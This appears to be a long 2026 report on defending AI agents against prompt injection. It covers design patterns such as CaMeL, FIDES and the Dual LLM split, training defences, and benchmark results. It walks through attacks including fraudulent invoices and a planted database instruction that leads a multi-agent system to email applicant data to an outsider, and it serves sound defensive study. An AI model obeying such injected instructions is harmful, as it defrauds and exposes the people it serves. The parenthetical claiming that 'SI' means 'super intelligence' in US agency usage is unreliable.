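The agencies illustrate privilege risk with an imaginary procurement agent. An organisation gives it broad access to financial systems, email and contracts, and reviews its permissions only at the start. Other agents come to trust its outputs. An attacker then compromises a minor tool in its workflow, inherits the agent's privileges, changes contracts and approves payments. No alert goes off, and the logs look legitimate because a trusted agent took every action.

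Almost every step in the story depends on a familiar failure, such as excessive permissions or misplaced trust between systems, which supports the case for ordinary security practice. The agencies' general advice also supports it. They regard AI systems as fundamentally IT systems and tell organisations to manage agents within established security frameworks instead of creating a separate discipline.

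The same agencies say that organisations "should only use agentic AI for low-risk and non-sensitive tasks". Taken literally, this advice would keep an agent from paying invoices on its own. They also note that governance designed for people does not always transfer to agents, and that gaps in current evaluation methods can make reliable validation "nearly impossible". These statements strongly support the view that the attack surface can't be bounded.

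The two recommendations are compatible, because one concerns how to manage the risk and the other how much risk to accept while the methods are immature. The agencies tell organisations to assume that agents may behave unexpectedly until practices, evaluations and standards mature, which suggests that the restriction could loosen. They also describe approval steps for high-impact actions, which would have little purpose if agents were never used for such actions.

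Supporters of ordinary practice who cite the agencies' advice on frameworks must also acknowledge its restriction. The agencies endorse the method, but not, at present, for the sensitive work that many firms most want to automate. An insurer following this advice closely could let an agent read invoices and prepare payments, as long as the invoices were not sensitive and a person released the money.

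### How far the standards have come

In January 2026 NIST asked how to secure agents and received more than 80 substantive comments. The most common position, according to Wallsten and Oh Lam, was that NIST should extend its existing frameworks instead of building new ones. Many commenters also wanted at least one fixed control outside the model. In NIST's own *Summary Analysis of Responses to the Request for Information Regarding Security Considerations*, Riggs, Hamin and colleagues (2026) found wide agreement that agents pose novel threats, that security concerns are a barrier to adoption, and that basic security principles still apply but need adapting. Many of the commenters sell agents or security products, so the responses are informed opinion rather than tests of whether the controls work.

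Incident response needs adapting for agents. Anthropic and Microsoft told NIST that existing definitions of an incident don't fit an authorised agent that causes harm. In October, NIST, NSA and CISA's *Key Practices for Incident Readiness and Response* (2026) set out ten voluntary practices, mainly for organisations that train or evaluate highly capable agents. It defines a control incident as one in which an agent takes significant actions that neither its operator nor an adversary instructed. The unauthorised renewal might qualify if it were significant enough. A payment redirected by an attacker's instruction would not, so a firm needs to plan for both kinds of incident.

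NIST also runs an AI Agent Standards Initiative, and several pieces of its work on agents are still in progress:

- **Identity:** Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026), in *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, proposed a project in February on applying identity standards to agents. The proposal drew more than 600 formal responses, according to Galluzzo (2026), in *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity*. NIST published a set of design tenets in October, but the project's web page, NCCoE's *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization*, still invites comments on its scope and feasibility. (SI stands for "super intelligence", the term US agencies now use for AI.)
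- **Security profile:** in a May discussion essay, NIST (2026) was still weighing whether its cybersecurity profile for AI should cover agents in one place or throughout.
- **Attack taxonomy:** NIST's *Adversarial Machine Learning* (2026), a draft classification of attacks on agents and ways to mitigate them, is open for comment until 18 December.

NIST and CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, have already finished guidance on issuing, verifying and revoking access tokens in federal cloud systems (Jadhav, September 2026, *NIST and CISA finalize token security guidance for federal cloud systems*). OWASP, a nonprofit known for its lists of common software vulnerabilities, has published a Top 10 for Agentic Applications, which firms can use to plan tests.

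Standards for agent authorisation are less settled. OpenAI refers readers to an internet draft, *AI Agent Authentication and Authorization*, but notes that it is an individual proposal, not an Internet Engineering Task Force standard. Other specifications aim to ensure that each agent in a chain passes on less authority than it received. The insurer can build most of the controls with existing protocols, but it can't yet point its supervisor to a settled standard that covers them all.

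Wallsten and Oh Lam expect courts to treat even a voluntary NIST standard as a benchmark for reasonable care, and insurers to use it when they decide whom to cover.

The case for ordinary practice also assumes that organisations carry it out, and many struggle to. Much of the advice on agents rests on zero trust, the principle of verifying everything that tries to access an organisation's systems. GAO's *Agencies Need to Fully Address Federal Guidance* (2026), a report by the US government's audit office, found that 17 of 22 federal agencies had not fully addressed official guidance in their zero-trust plans. Officials blamed limited staff and funding, among other things. The audit examined plans, not breaches, and private firms may do better. But a firm that has never removed its old accounts and surplus permissions would be deploying agents in the conditions that the six agencies describe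 in their procurement scenario.

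## The case for designs in which the model cannot authorise actions

Even well-set permissions leave a gap, because they cover a tool and the limits on its use, but not where the values in a particular request came from. Suppose the insurer's agent may email payment records to outside auditors, whose addresses change too often for a fixed list. The agent should use an auditor's address that the clerk types in, but an address it picks up from a supplier's invoice may belong to a thief. Both emails would use the same tool and credential and go to a valid address, so software can tell them apart only if it has tracked where the address came from.

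In *An Organization-Scoped LLM Agent Runtime Architecture for Regulated Cybersecurity Operations*, Fatouros, Makridis and colleagues (2026) propose a system for security teams at financial firms that checks the user's role, the permitted tools and the scope of the data at every step. They acknowledge that these checks do not stop "tool calls with valid arguments acting on attacker-influenced inputs", so they add injection detectors and human review. Critics of permissions want a firmer safeguard than a detector, in which ordinary software works out which data influenced an action and refuses the action if the wrong data did.

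Most of this work changes the software around the model. Other researchers propose changing the model itself so that it separates instructions from data, or giving it fewer decisions to make.

### Two models and a controller

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed dividing an assistant between two models. A privileged model takes the user's request and can use tools, but never sees untrusted content. A quarantined model reads the untrusted content but has no tools, and the design assumes that an attacker may control whatever it outputs. A controller, which is ordinary software, passes work between them. If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the steps are:

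1. The privileged model asks for the email. The controller fetches it and stores it under the name $VAR1.
2. The privileged model asks for a summary of $VAR1. The controller gives the text to the quarantined model and stores the answer as $VAR2.
3. The privileged model tells the controller to display $VAR2 to the user.

The privileged model sees only the names of the variables, so instructions in the email cannot reach it. Willison allowed one exception, for cases where the quarantined model has to choose from a fixed set of categories. The controller can then check that the answer is one of them and pass it to the privileged model.

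Willison called this solution "pretty bad". It is complicated to build, and a single mistake that lets untrusted text reach the privileged model removes its protection. The quarantined model could also write a summary that persuades the user to paste private data into a hostile website.

The pattern has another weakness. Suppose the user asks the assistant to send a contract to the address given in the latest email. Hostile text can make the quarantined model return a different address, and the privileged model then sends the contract there, seeing only the placeholder $VAR2. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) explains that separating the models protects an agent's control flow (which actions it takes and in what order) but not necessarily its data flow (the values that pass from one action to the next).

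### CaMeL

Google DeepMind's CaMeL, introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), keeps the two models and adds a check on the data. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how it works:

1. The privileged model reads the trusted request and writes a complete program for the task in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter runs the program. Only the interpreter can call tools.
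3. When the program needs something from untrusted text, the interpreter calls the quarantined model and stores its answer in a variable.
4. The interpreter tags each value with its sources and with the people who may read it.
5. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, which is a short function that examines the tool, its arguments and their tags, and then allows or denies the call.

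The program gives CaMeL what *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) calls control-flow integrity. Untrusted data can affect which of the program's branches the interpreter takes, but it cannot add a new one. If the program pays invoices below a certain amount and refers the rest to staff, an attacker can choose between those outcomes by changing the amount on an invoice, but can't make the agent delete the vendor register, because no branch does that.

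How well CaMeL protects the data depends on its policies. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), a formal model of agents, gives an example where the program sets an email's subject and body and asks the quarantined model only for the sender's address. Hostile text can't change the subject or body, but it could corrupt the address, and only a policy would catch that.

### An invoice in the interpreter

Suppose the clerk asks the agent to pay the latest invoice from Brook Cleaning, the contractor whose invoice carries the false bank details. Leave aside payment limits and staff approval for the moment. The privileged model might write this program, in which `extract` calls the quarantined model:

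```
invoice = latest_invoice("Brook Cleaning")
details = extract(invoice, ["amount"])
vendor  = register_lookup("Brook Cleaning")
pay(account = vendor.account, amount = details.amount)
```

The interpreter tags the values as it runs:

| Value | Sources |
|---|---|
| "Brook Cleaning" | clerk's request |
| details.amount | email, clerk's request |
| vendor.account | vendor register, clerk's request |

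The insurer's policy requires the account to come from the register, with no influence from an email:

```
policy for pay(account, amount):
    if "vendor register" not in account.sources: deny
    if "email" in account.sources: deny
    allow
```

The attacker's sentence about new bank details has no effect on this program, because the program never takes an account number from the invoice. But the privileged model could have written a worse program that extracts the account number along with the amount and calls `pay(account = details.account, ...)`. The interpreter would block that call because the account number is tagged as coming from an email. The policy checks only the tags, so the wording of the email makes no difference.

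Nikolaou and colleagues' own system, CaMeLoT, could reject the bad program before it ran. It converts the program into a map of every path execution could take and checks each path against the firm's rules. If a path breaks a rule, CaMeLoT describes that path to the privileged model, which tries to write a better program. CaMeLoT can also enforce rules about order, such as requiring an approval before a payment. The map simplifies loops, so CaMeLoT sometimes rejects a safe program.

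A bank interface that pays only registered accounts would also have stopped this fraud. Tracking sources helps more when the clerk asks the agent to pay all the morning's invoices, because the program must then identify the supplier for each one. If it takes the supplier's name from the email, a fraudster can name a different registered supplier. The register then returns a genuine account, and the bank's interface accepts it. The interpreter blocks the payment because the email influenced which account the program looked up, but it also blocks honest invoices for the same reason. The insurer could fix this by having the program start from the insurer's list of open purchase orders and look for an invoice to match each one, so that the supplier's name comes from a trusted source.

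The policy does nothing about a false amount. If Brook Cleaning did $18,400 of work but bills for $81,400, the account is correct and the insurer overpays by $63,000. Nikolaou and colleagues give a sample rule for money transfers under which neither the recipient nor the amount may come from an untrusted source. Here that rule would block every payment, because the amounts come from invoices. It makes more sense to have the program look up the purchase order, pass it to `pay` as a third argument, and add these lines to the policy before `allow`:

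```
    if "purchasing system" not in order.sources: deny
    if "email" in order.sources: deny
    if amount > order.unpaid_balance: deny
```

The amount still comes from the email, but it can no longer exceed what the insurer agreed to pay. The supplier could still bill the full $18,400 for work it never did. The policy would also need a record of the work to catch that.

### FIDES and its labels

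CaMeL's privileged model writes its program before it sees any results, which is awkward when the right next step depends on what an email says. Microsoft's FIDES keeps the ordinary agent loop, in which the model chooses one step at a time. It uses information-flow control, which means it labels everything that passes through the loop by source and sensitivity, and blocks actions that would combine labels in forbidden ways (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025, *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*).

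In FIDES, each piece of data has an integrity label, trusted or untrusted, and a confidentiality label that lists who may read it. Anything derived from several pieces gets the most restrictive combination of their labels. For example, if Ana, Ben and Carla may read one document and Ben, Carla and Dev may read another, only Ben and Carla may read a summary of both, and the summary is untrusted if either document is.

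Two basic policies use these labels. Under the integrity policy, a tool call with serious consequences may go ahead only if trusted data alone influenced the choice of tool and its arguments. Under the confidentiality policy, data may leave the system only if every recipient is allowed to read it. This policy doesn't prevent prompt injection by itself, but it limits what an injection can leak.

The integrity policy would soon stop an ordinary agent from doing any useful work. Once the model reads an untrusted email, its context is untrusted, and so is every request it makes afterwards. FIDES avoids this by hiding untrusted values in variables, as in Willison's pattern, but only those that would change the context's label. If an email's timestamp is trusted and its body isn't, the model sees the timestamp, with a variable name in place of the body.

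Sometimes the agent's next step depends on the content of a hidden value. For example, a user might ask the agent to check three emails and create a calendar event if one of them requests a meeting. FIDES can query a quarantined model about whether there is a request and restrict the answer to true or false. The answer is still untrusted, but its label records that it carries only one bit, which is too little to contain an instruction, so a policy may allow the agent to act on it. A second query then extracts the meeting details and passes them to the calendar tool without adding them to the main model's context.

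Even a one-bit answer can be enough for an attack to succeed. If the question is whether a manager has approved an invoice, a fraudster only needs the answer "yes". The insurer would have to keep such shortcuts for questions where it can tolerate a wrong answer.

Costa and colleagues prove a formal guarantee called explicit secrecy, which means that confidential data cannot flow directly into anything an outsider can see. It doesn't cover what an outsider can infer from the agent's choices or timing. For example, if the agent emails a supplier only when the insurer is short of cash, the email's arrival can reveal the shortage even if the text doesn't mention it. The guarantee also assumes that the labels are right and the user's messages, the agent's configuration and the tool descriptions are trustworthy.

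### Simpler patterns

Some agents do not need an interpreter or a labelling system. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes six designs based on the principle that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger any consequential action.

| Pattern | How it works | What hostile text can still change |
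|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model turns a request into one of a fixed set of actions and never sees the results | Nothing, unless it is in the request itself |
| Plan-then-execute | The model fixes the list of tool calls before reading untrusted text | The contents of a planned call, such as the body of an email |
| Map-reduce | A separate model without tools reads each document and gives a restricted answer; a further step combines the answers | The answer about its own document |
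| Dual LLM | A privileged model plans and a quarantined model reads | The values the quarantined model returns |
| Code-then-execute | The model writes a program that calls tools and quarantined models, as in CaMeL | The values the program handles |
| Context minimisation | The system removes the user's prompt from the context before the model writes its reply | The first step, such as a database query, but not the reply |

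The paper illustrates map-reduce with an agent that searches a folder for this month's invoices and emails them to the accounts department. A model reads each file and reports only whether it is an invoice. An attacker could write a file that tricks the model into including it, but could have achieved the same result with a fake invoice.

These patterns deliberately stop an agent from doing arbitrary tasks. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think general-purpose agents are unlikely to offer reliable guarantees while built on the current kind of language model, so they ask which narrower agents would still be useful.

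Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) is simpler still. Until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of three properties in a session: it can process untrustworthy input, it can access sensitive systems or private data, and it can change state or communicate externally. If it needs all three, a person or another reliable check must supervise it. The rule resembles Willison's lethal trifecta, but it also counts changes of state, so it covers redirected payments as well as stolen data.

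The accounts-payable agent has all three properties. The insurer could remove the first by accepting invoices only from trusted senders, but that fails if an attacker has broken into a supplier's mailbox. It could instead restrict the third by paying only registered accounts. Similarly, Meta treats an email agent as compliant if it can write only to trusted recipients or if a person checks each draft. An agent can also change configuration partway through a session. For example, it could browse the web without access to private data, then permanently lose its ability to communicate before it opens internal systems.

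The rule is easy to apply, but it can't distinguish payments that an email influenced from other payments. Meta presents the rule as a supplement to least privilege, and warns that a compliant agent can still make mistakes and that users may approve a warning without reading it.

### What the proofs assume

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) defines precisely what such designs guarantee and gives machine-checked proofs about agents that fix their plan before they read untrusted content. Dongol compares each agent with an imaginary one that follows the same plan under the same controls but never obeys untrusted text. The real agent is secure if an injection can't make it reveal anything about the user's data that the imaginary agent wouldn't also reveal in response to some message. Suppose a user authorises an assistant to send her calendar to anyone who requests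 a meeting. An injected order to send the calendar isn't a leak, because a genuine request would have had the same result, but an order to add her password reset code is a leak, because no message would make the imaginary agent send it.

The main theorem concerns a "fence", a control that withdraws tools. An agent is secure for any plan if, when it first reads untrusted content, the monitor permanently withdraws every tool an injection could call. The proof assumes that each injection triggers a single tool call, that secrets don't affect when the model obeys an injection, and that the attacker sees the content and order of messages but not their timing. The monitor has to withdraw the tools early because if the agent reads an email, looks up a private account number and only then loses its ability to send, an injection can make it send the number first. But an agent that has to reply to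 the email can't use such a fence, because it would lose the ability to send.

Human approval is one way around this, but Dongol shows that its protection depends on what the user approves. If a user approves "the next email" after the agent has read a hostile message, an injected email can go out first and use up the approval. If the user approves the exact text and recipient, an injected email can go out only if it matches both. The insurer's software should therefore restrict the agent to the exact account and amount that staff approved.

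Dongol also points out a loophole in the definition. A plan might let an outsider guess a secret code once and then report whether the guess was right. For any two possible codes, some guess would tell them apart, so an injection that reveals the whole code counts as no new leak under the definition. The proofs also cover only leaks. They don't apply to a redirected payment, which sends money to the wrong place without necessarily revealing any data, and they don't show that the plan itself is correct.

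The theorems hold only if the deployed system meets seven conditions:

- Trusted software runs the plan, so the model can't skip or alter a step.
- The model can reach tools and untrusted sources only through the monitor.
- Untrusted content enters the context only after the monitor has allowed the read.
- A refused request has no effect that the attacker can see.
- The attacker can't see the monitor's state or the agent's internal steps.
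- A new session erases everything the model kept from untrusted content.
- The attacker can't write to any source that the system treats as trusted.

The last condition is easy to break by accident. Dongol's example is a calendar that can't count as a trusted source because it accepts invitations from outsiders. The insurer's vendor register has the same problem if staff update it from emailed forms without checking them. A false account number would then carry the tag "vendor register", and the interpreter would pay it. CaMeL and FIDES depend on this condition as much as Dongol's agents do.

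CaMeL can also fail when agents work together. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three agents, each protected by CaMeL. One read a database of job applicants, one sent messages, and an orchestrator assigned their tasks. The researchers planted an instruction in the database. The orchestrator correctly treated the database's contents as untrusted, but it included a summary of them in its request to the messaging agent. That agent treated the whole request as coming from its user, so its privileged model read the planted instruction and added a step that emailed the applicants' data to an outsider.

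The researchers had switched off the policies on tool calls to isolate the problem. A policy based on sources might not have helped, because the outsider's address now appeared in the messaging agent's own program, which the interpreter treats as trusted. A fixed list of permitted recipients would have stopped the email. Peters-Gill and colleagues propose sending instructions and untrusted data between agents through separate channels, so that the data keeps its label. An insurer that used one agent to read invoices and another to pay them would need the same precaution.

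### Marking data inside the model

All these designs leave the model unchanged. The alternative is to train the model to recognise which text it may obey. *StruQ* (2024) uses a front end that puts the developer's prompt and the untrusted data into separate parts of the input. As *ResumeShield* (2026) explains, the method reserves special delimiter tokens for the system's designer and trains the model to follow only instructions in the prompt. *Intent-Aware Protection for AI Agents* (2026) describes a related method, the instruction hierarchy, which trains a model to prioritise instructions from more privileged sources.

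*SecAlign* (2024) trains the model on pairs of good and bad answers. In one example, the instruction asks for a Python function, and the data describes a test for prime numbers and then asks whether dinosaurs exist. Training rewards the model for writing the function and penalises it for answering the dinosaur question. A program can create these examples by joining pieces of text, without human labellers. *Meta-SecAlign* (2025), the successor to *SecAlign* for agents, cut the share of attacks that succeeded in AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, travel, banking and messaging tasks, from 14.7% to 1.9%.

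*ASIDE* (Zverev, Kortukov and colleagues, 2025) changes how the model represents text. A language model turns each token into a long list of numbers called an embedding, and normally a token gets the same embedding whether it appears in an instruction or in data. ASIDE takes the numbers in a data token's embedding two at a time and rotates each pair by 90 degrees. If the embedding of "pay" began (3, 1) in an instruction, it would begin (−1, 3) in an email treated as data. The software marks each token as instruction or data before the model runs, and no wording in the email can change that.

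After this change, the researchers trained the models on ordinary instructions, without any examples of attacks. The models became better at ignoring instructions in data, and attacks succeeded less often on every indirect injection benchmark the researchers used, though many still worked. The tests covered single exchanges, whereas an agent may make hundreds of tool calls.

*On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* helps to explain why clearly marking untrusted text isn't enough. Part of its proof concerns guessing whether the model's internal numbers came from trusted or untrusted text. If both are equally common, the best possible guess is wrong with probability ½(1 − TV), where TV runs from 0, when the two kinds of numbers look identical, to 1, when they never overlap. With TV at 0.9, the best guess is wrong 5% of the time. ASIDE pushes the two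 kinds apart, at least at the input. But the proof also relies on untrusted text passing through the same computation that chooses the model's actions. ASIDE doesn't change that, so untrusted text can still influence those actions even when the model can distinguish it from trusted text.

The theorem does not apply to models that process trusted and untrusted text in separate encoders, or that block untrusted text from the parts of the computation that control actions. Such designs were still largely an ambition in mid-2026. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) lists "non-executable data blocks" and attention mechanisms that track sources among research directions. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) concludes that nobody can enforce the separation inside the model, so software outside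 it must. This conclusion goes further than the theorem, which does not rule out enforcement in models built differently, but it fairly describes the models that firms can use today.

For a regulated firm, changing the model has two further drawbacks. *ResumeShield* notes that these methods require the ability to train the model, and an insurer that rents one from a supplier usually can't train it. Also, a model that never obeyed an instruction in an email could still accept false bank details from one. Training makes attacks rarer and the quarantined model more reliable, but it can't replace the policy on payments.

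### Using less of the model

Much of the invoice agent's work needs no language model. Looking up a supplier, comparing two amounts and ordering a payment are jobs that conventional software has done for decades. In a fixed workflow, programmers write the sequence of steps in advance, and the model handles only the steps that involve interpreting language. *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (2025) similarly notes that in systems that plan before acting, ordinary code can carry out the plan.

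*Position* (Singh, Bastos and Mulang', 2026) argues that for most structured business tasks, small language models should extract information from documents, while databases and explicit rules make the decisions. Larger models would help write those rules beforehand but take no part in the live process. The paper bases its case on cost, reliability and ease of governance, not on prompt injection. But the design also limits what an injection can do, because the model that reads the documents has no tools and does not decide what happens next.

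Such a system provably makes mistakes no more often than its extraction step does, provided the rules are right and the database returns correct facts. If the model misreads one invoice in 200, at most 0.5% of the results are wrong. The insurer couldn't rely on that figure under attack, because a fraudster can write an invoice so that the model misreads it. The workflow therefore still needs the same checks on the account and amount as the CaMeL version.

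A fixed workflow has control-flow integrity without relying on a model to write a correct program for each request. The sequence stays the same until someone changes it, so the insurer's engineers can review it once, test it and show it to a supervisor. The guarantee assumes that the code is correct and that it accepts the model's output only in the expected form. In exchange, the insurer gives up having an agent, meaning a system in which the model chooses the actions.

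A fixed workflow is only a small limitation when paying routine invoices. It is a much greater one in open-ended work, such as explaining a rise in claims costs, because it can supply standard reports but can't select what to examine next.

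## How often attacks succeed against current models

A firm would need fewer restrictions on its agents if the model almost never followed hostile instructions. AI companies pursue this through model-level defences, which use training, prompting or filtering to make the model itself resist such instructions. They usually report the result as an attack success rate, which is the share of attempts, or of attacked tasks, in which the attacker succeeds. The two shares can differ widely, since an attacker who fails 99 times on a single task and then succeeds has a success rate of 1% by attempts and 100% by tasks.

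### Two experiments from 2025

*Security Challenges in AI Agent Deployment* (2025) describes a public competition that the security company Gray Swan held in March and April 2025, with sponsorship from the UK AI Security Institute and several AI companies. Almost 2,000 people competed for $171,800 in prizes by attacking agents built on 22 models in 44 simulated workplaces. The agents had simulated tools, such as one for looking up medical records, and rules for using them. Participants could see how an agent responded and revise their attacks.

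Participants made about 1.8 million attempts, and about 62,000 (3.4%) succeeded. The paper reports an overall rate of 12.7% because it divides successes by user sessions, and a session could include several attempts. Counted by session, attacks typed directly into the chat succeeded 5.7% of the time and indirect ones 27.1%. For actions that the rules prohibited, the rates were 4.2% and 36.8%. Every model eventually broke its rules in every way the organisers had targeted.

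The organisers then replayed 4,700 of the best attacks, unchanged, on 19 models. A single try produced violations for 20% to 60% of the targeted behaviours, depending on the model, and ten tries raised the rate to nearly 100% for most models. Many attacks worked on models they hadn't been written for, so an attacker can develop an attack on one model and use it against another.

*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) retested 12 published defences, some against prompt injection and some against jailbreaks. Their developers had mostly tested them against fixed lists of known attacks or weak automated attacks. In the retests, attackers wrote a text, saw how close it came to working, and revised it to suit each defence. Some attackers were algorithms with large computing budgets, and others were people, including more than 500 in an online competition.

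Most of the defences failed against adaptive attacks. Two methods that use prompting to keep the model on the user's task had let through as few as 1% of the fixed attacks in the AgentDojo benchmark, but both failed more than 95% of the time against an adaptive search. The attack success rate against Meta-SecAlign, the specially trained model, rose from about 2% on AgentDojo to 96% under adaptive attack. Three of the four detectors tested let through more than 90% of adaptive attacks, and the fourth let through 71%. On a subset of the scenarios, the automated search succeeded in 69% of cases, and the human attackers collectively succeeded in all of them.

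These figures measure what a determined attacker can achieve with time and feedback, not how often a fraudster's first email works. Nasr and colleagues still consider detectors useful against unsophisticated attacks.

### Scores in late 2026

Models have improved a great deal since then. Some of the most detailed figures come from Anthropic's September 2026 *System Card* for Claude Fable 5.1. One test uses a fixed set of 1,804 attacks, which Gray Swan selected from its competitions, in 37 scenarios where the agent writes code, calls tools or operates a graphical desktop. Only 0.1% of single attempts succeeded against Fable 5.1, and an attacker with 15 attempts had a 1.0% chance of at least one success. For the best model from another company, Google's Gemini 3.7 Flash, the chance with 15 attempts was 9.2%, and for most of the others it was between 24% and 53%.

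Fable 5.1 did much worse against Shade, an automated attacker from Gray Swan. Shade learns by trial and error on the 40 coding scenarios used in the test, then makes 200 attempts at each. The newest version of Shade succeeded in 57% of its attempts against Fable 5.1, and at least once in 38 of the 40 scenarios. Anthropic then switched on its probes, which inspect the results of tool calls for injected instructions before the model acts on them. Shade's success rate fell to 13%, but it still succeeded at least once in 36 scenarios.

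Anthropic describes this as a highly permissive test, because real attackers rarely know the target deployment and risk being detected with each attempt. That is fair for an insurer's private system, but less so for a widely sold coding agent, which an attacker can buy and practise on.

All the successful attacks in that test came through an older model, Claude Opus 4.8. A classifier that looks for hacking-related content had diverted about 64% of requests to it. None of the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered led to a successful attack. This is encouraging, but the classifier may have diverted the most dangerous requests. Customers also get the combined system, not Fable 5.1 alone.

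In a third test, an agent used a web browser in 110 environments containing attacks that testers had developed against an earlier Claude model. With ten attempts per environment, 2.6% of attempts succeeded against Fable 5.1. None succeeded once Anthropic turned on auto mode, which combines the probes with a second classifier that blocks dangerous tool calls.

Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, dated 22 September, reports that the model performed similarly to or better than its predecessor, Opus 5, on every injection test. It also warns that the new model is more likely than earlier ones to follow some malicious instructions.

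OpenAI reported in October that GPT-6 Sol resisted 99.99% of direct prompt injections and 97.13% of indirect ones (Cross, 2026, *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*). The indirect figure matters more for an agent that reads strangers' email, and 2.87% of those attacks still succeeded. Such a percentage means little without knowing how many tries the attacker had, how well the attacker could adapt and which tools the agent had.

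An outside benchmark covers newer models from Google, OpenAI and Anthropic together. PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach* takes long office tasks, such as analysing a bond portfolio and recommending a trading strategy, and builds attacks into them in advance. The attacks aim at goals such as stealing data or installing ransomware, so the agents hold tools that make such damage possible. Software checks whether the attack worked. The results, for five attempts per case (k = 5), include:

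| Model | Developer | Attack success rate, by test case |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 4 Carbon | Google | 2.4% |
| Gemini 4 Argon | Google | 4.3% |
| GPT-6 Astra | OpenAI | 7.6% |
| Claude Fable 5.2 | Anthropic | 10.0% |
| Muse Wonder | Meta | 15.2% |
| Kimi K3.1 Pro | Moonshot | 50.0% |
| Grok 4.5 | xAI | 91.4% |

PromptArmor sells AI security, so it benefits when agents look vulnerable, and it advertises the benchmark as the one with the highest success rates against leading models. The margins of error are also wide enough that GPT-6 Astra and Fable 5.2 may be equally resistant. But a bias towards hard cases wouldn't explain why a few per cent of the attacks succeeded against one model and nine in ten against another, a difference that matters to a firm choosing a model.

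### One model, six scores

Claude Opus 5's scores depend heavily on the test. Anthropic's additional safeguards against injection were off in the Shade, Gray Swan and browser tests.

| Test | Attacker | What the agent operates | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Shade, computer use | Trained on the test scenarios | Graphical desktop | 0.18% of attempts |
| Gray Swan benchmark | Fixed attacks from competitions | Code, tools, graphical desktop | 0.4% of attempts |
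| Browser test | Fixed attacks developed on an older model | Web browser | 2.1% of attempts |
| Shade, coding, older version | Trained on the test scenarios | Coding environment | 2.7% of attempts |
| PromptArmor's benchmark | Attacks built into the task | Tools for office work | 10.0% of cases, k = 5 |
| Shade, coding, newer version | Trained for longer, on more varied attacks | Coding environment | 91% of attempts |

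The favorable result in the top row and the unfavorable one in the bottom row are both accurate, but the insurer can't use either to predict how its accounts-payable agent would fare, because none of these tests gave the agent the insurer's tools or suppliers.

Scores can change even when the model and the benchmark's name stay the same. In July, The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reported that an attacker with 15 attempts on Gray Swan's benchmark had a 2.0% chance of success against Opus 5. Anthropic's September card reports 4.8% on a version of the benchmark with nine more scenarios and 670 more attacks.

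Success rates depend as much on the attacker's skill as on the choice of scenarios. *AutoDojo* (2026) compared automated attackers given the same number of tries against the target. Against an undefended agent, the best earlier attacker succeeded 23.1% of the time and the new one 52.4%. With a filter called DataFilter, the rates fell to 5.7% and 33.4%. Testing the filter with only the earlier attackers would therefore have understated the new attacker's success rate by a factor of nearly six.

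Even a perfect score can be misleading. *The safety number that was zero until someone tried* (Heaton, 2026) describes a test of Claude Code's auto mode that Anthropic commissioned. An outside firm ran 72 scenarios ten times each, and no attack succeeded. If the 720 runs were independent, they would rule out a true success rate above about 0.4% with 95% confidence, but only for attacks like the ones in the test. The security researcher Johann Rehberger then designed an attack for this target, and it succeeded in roughly 60% to 80% of a small number of tries.

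A fair comparison would change only the model and hold the scenarios, tools, number of tries and attacker's effort constant. *Measuring Indirect Prompt Injection in AI Agents* (Salbego, 2026) proposes a similar method, based on a study of 14 models, in which the attacker adapts and the tester isolates one variable at a time.

### Does training on more attacks help?

Developers often use adversarial training, which trains a model to resist attacks found by an automated tool, as OpenAI did with its Atlas browser agent. A tool that finds more attacks may not produce a safer model. In November 2026, news reports described an experiment in which training on a larger collection of attacks left agents easier to hijack.

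In *PIPETTE*, He, Wang and colleagues (2026) ran two attack tools, RL-Hammer and PISmith, against two small open models on 560 practice tasks, and trained each model on what each tool found. The two training methods were imitation, in which the model copies recorded good behaviour, and reinforcement learning, in which it earns a reward for finishing the task without obeying the attacker. They then tested the trained models on 40 AgentDojo tasks with three unfamiliar attackers. One used fixed texts, and the other two rewrote their attacks over about 250 attempts per task. The table shows how many tasks the most successful attacker hijacked.

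| Model and training method | Trained on RL-Hammer's attacks | Trained on PISmith's attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-4B, reinforcement learning | 11 of 40 | 19 of 40 |
| Llama-8B, reinforcement learning | 10 of 40 | 11 of 40 |
| Llama-8B, imitation | 6 of 40 | 8 of 40 |
| Qwen3-4B, imitation | 6 of 40 | 5 of 40 |

PISmith found more attacks on both models, but training on its collection gave the weaker defence in three of the four comparisons. Two of those three are weak evidence, because on Llama-8B the collections were almost the same size (1,783 attacks and 1,671) and the results differed by only one or two tasks. On Qwen3-4B, where PISmith's collection was much larger (7,132 attacks against 4,282), one training method worked better with the smaller collection and the other worked slightly better with the larger.

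Training also did not make the agents worse at resisting attacks. Zorz (2026) points out in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* that the researchers chose those 40 tasks because simple attacks had already succeeded on them against an unprotected Qwen3-4B. Every trained version of that model therefore resisted attacks on more than half of the tasks where the original had failed.

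The evidence for the researchers' explanation is stronger than the headline result. They suspected that once an attack tool finds a trick that works, such as claiming that the user's task is already complete, it keeps rewording that trick. To check, they had a language model identify the strategies in each collection of attacks and rate from 0 to 1 how well these accounted for attacks outside it. As the collections grew, RL-Hammer's score levelled off early, at about 0.20 on Qwen3-4B and 0.35 on Llama-8B, and PISmith's stalled or fell, because additional attacks from the same tool mostly repeated earlier ones.

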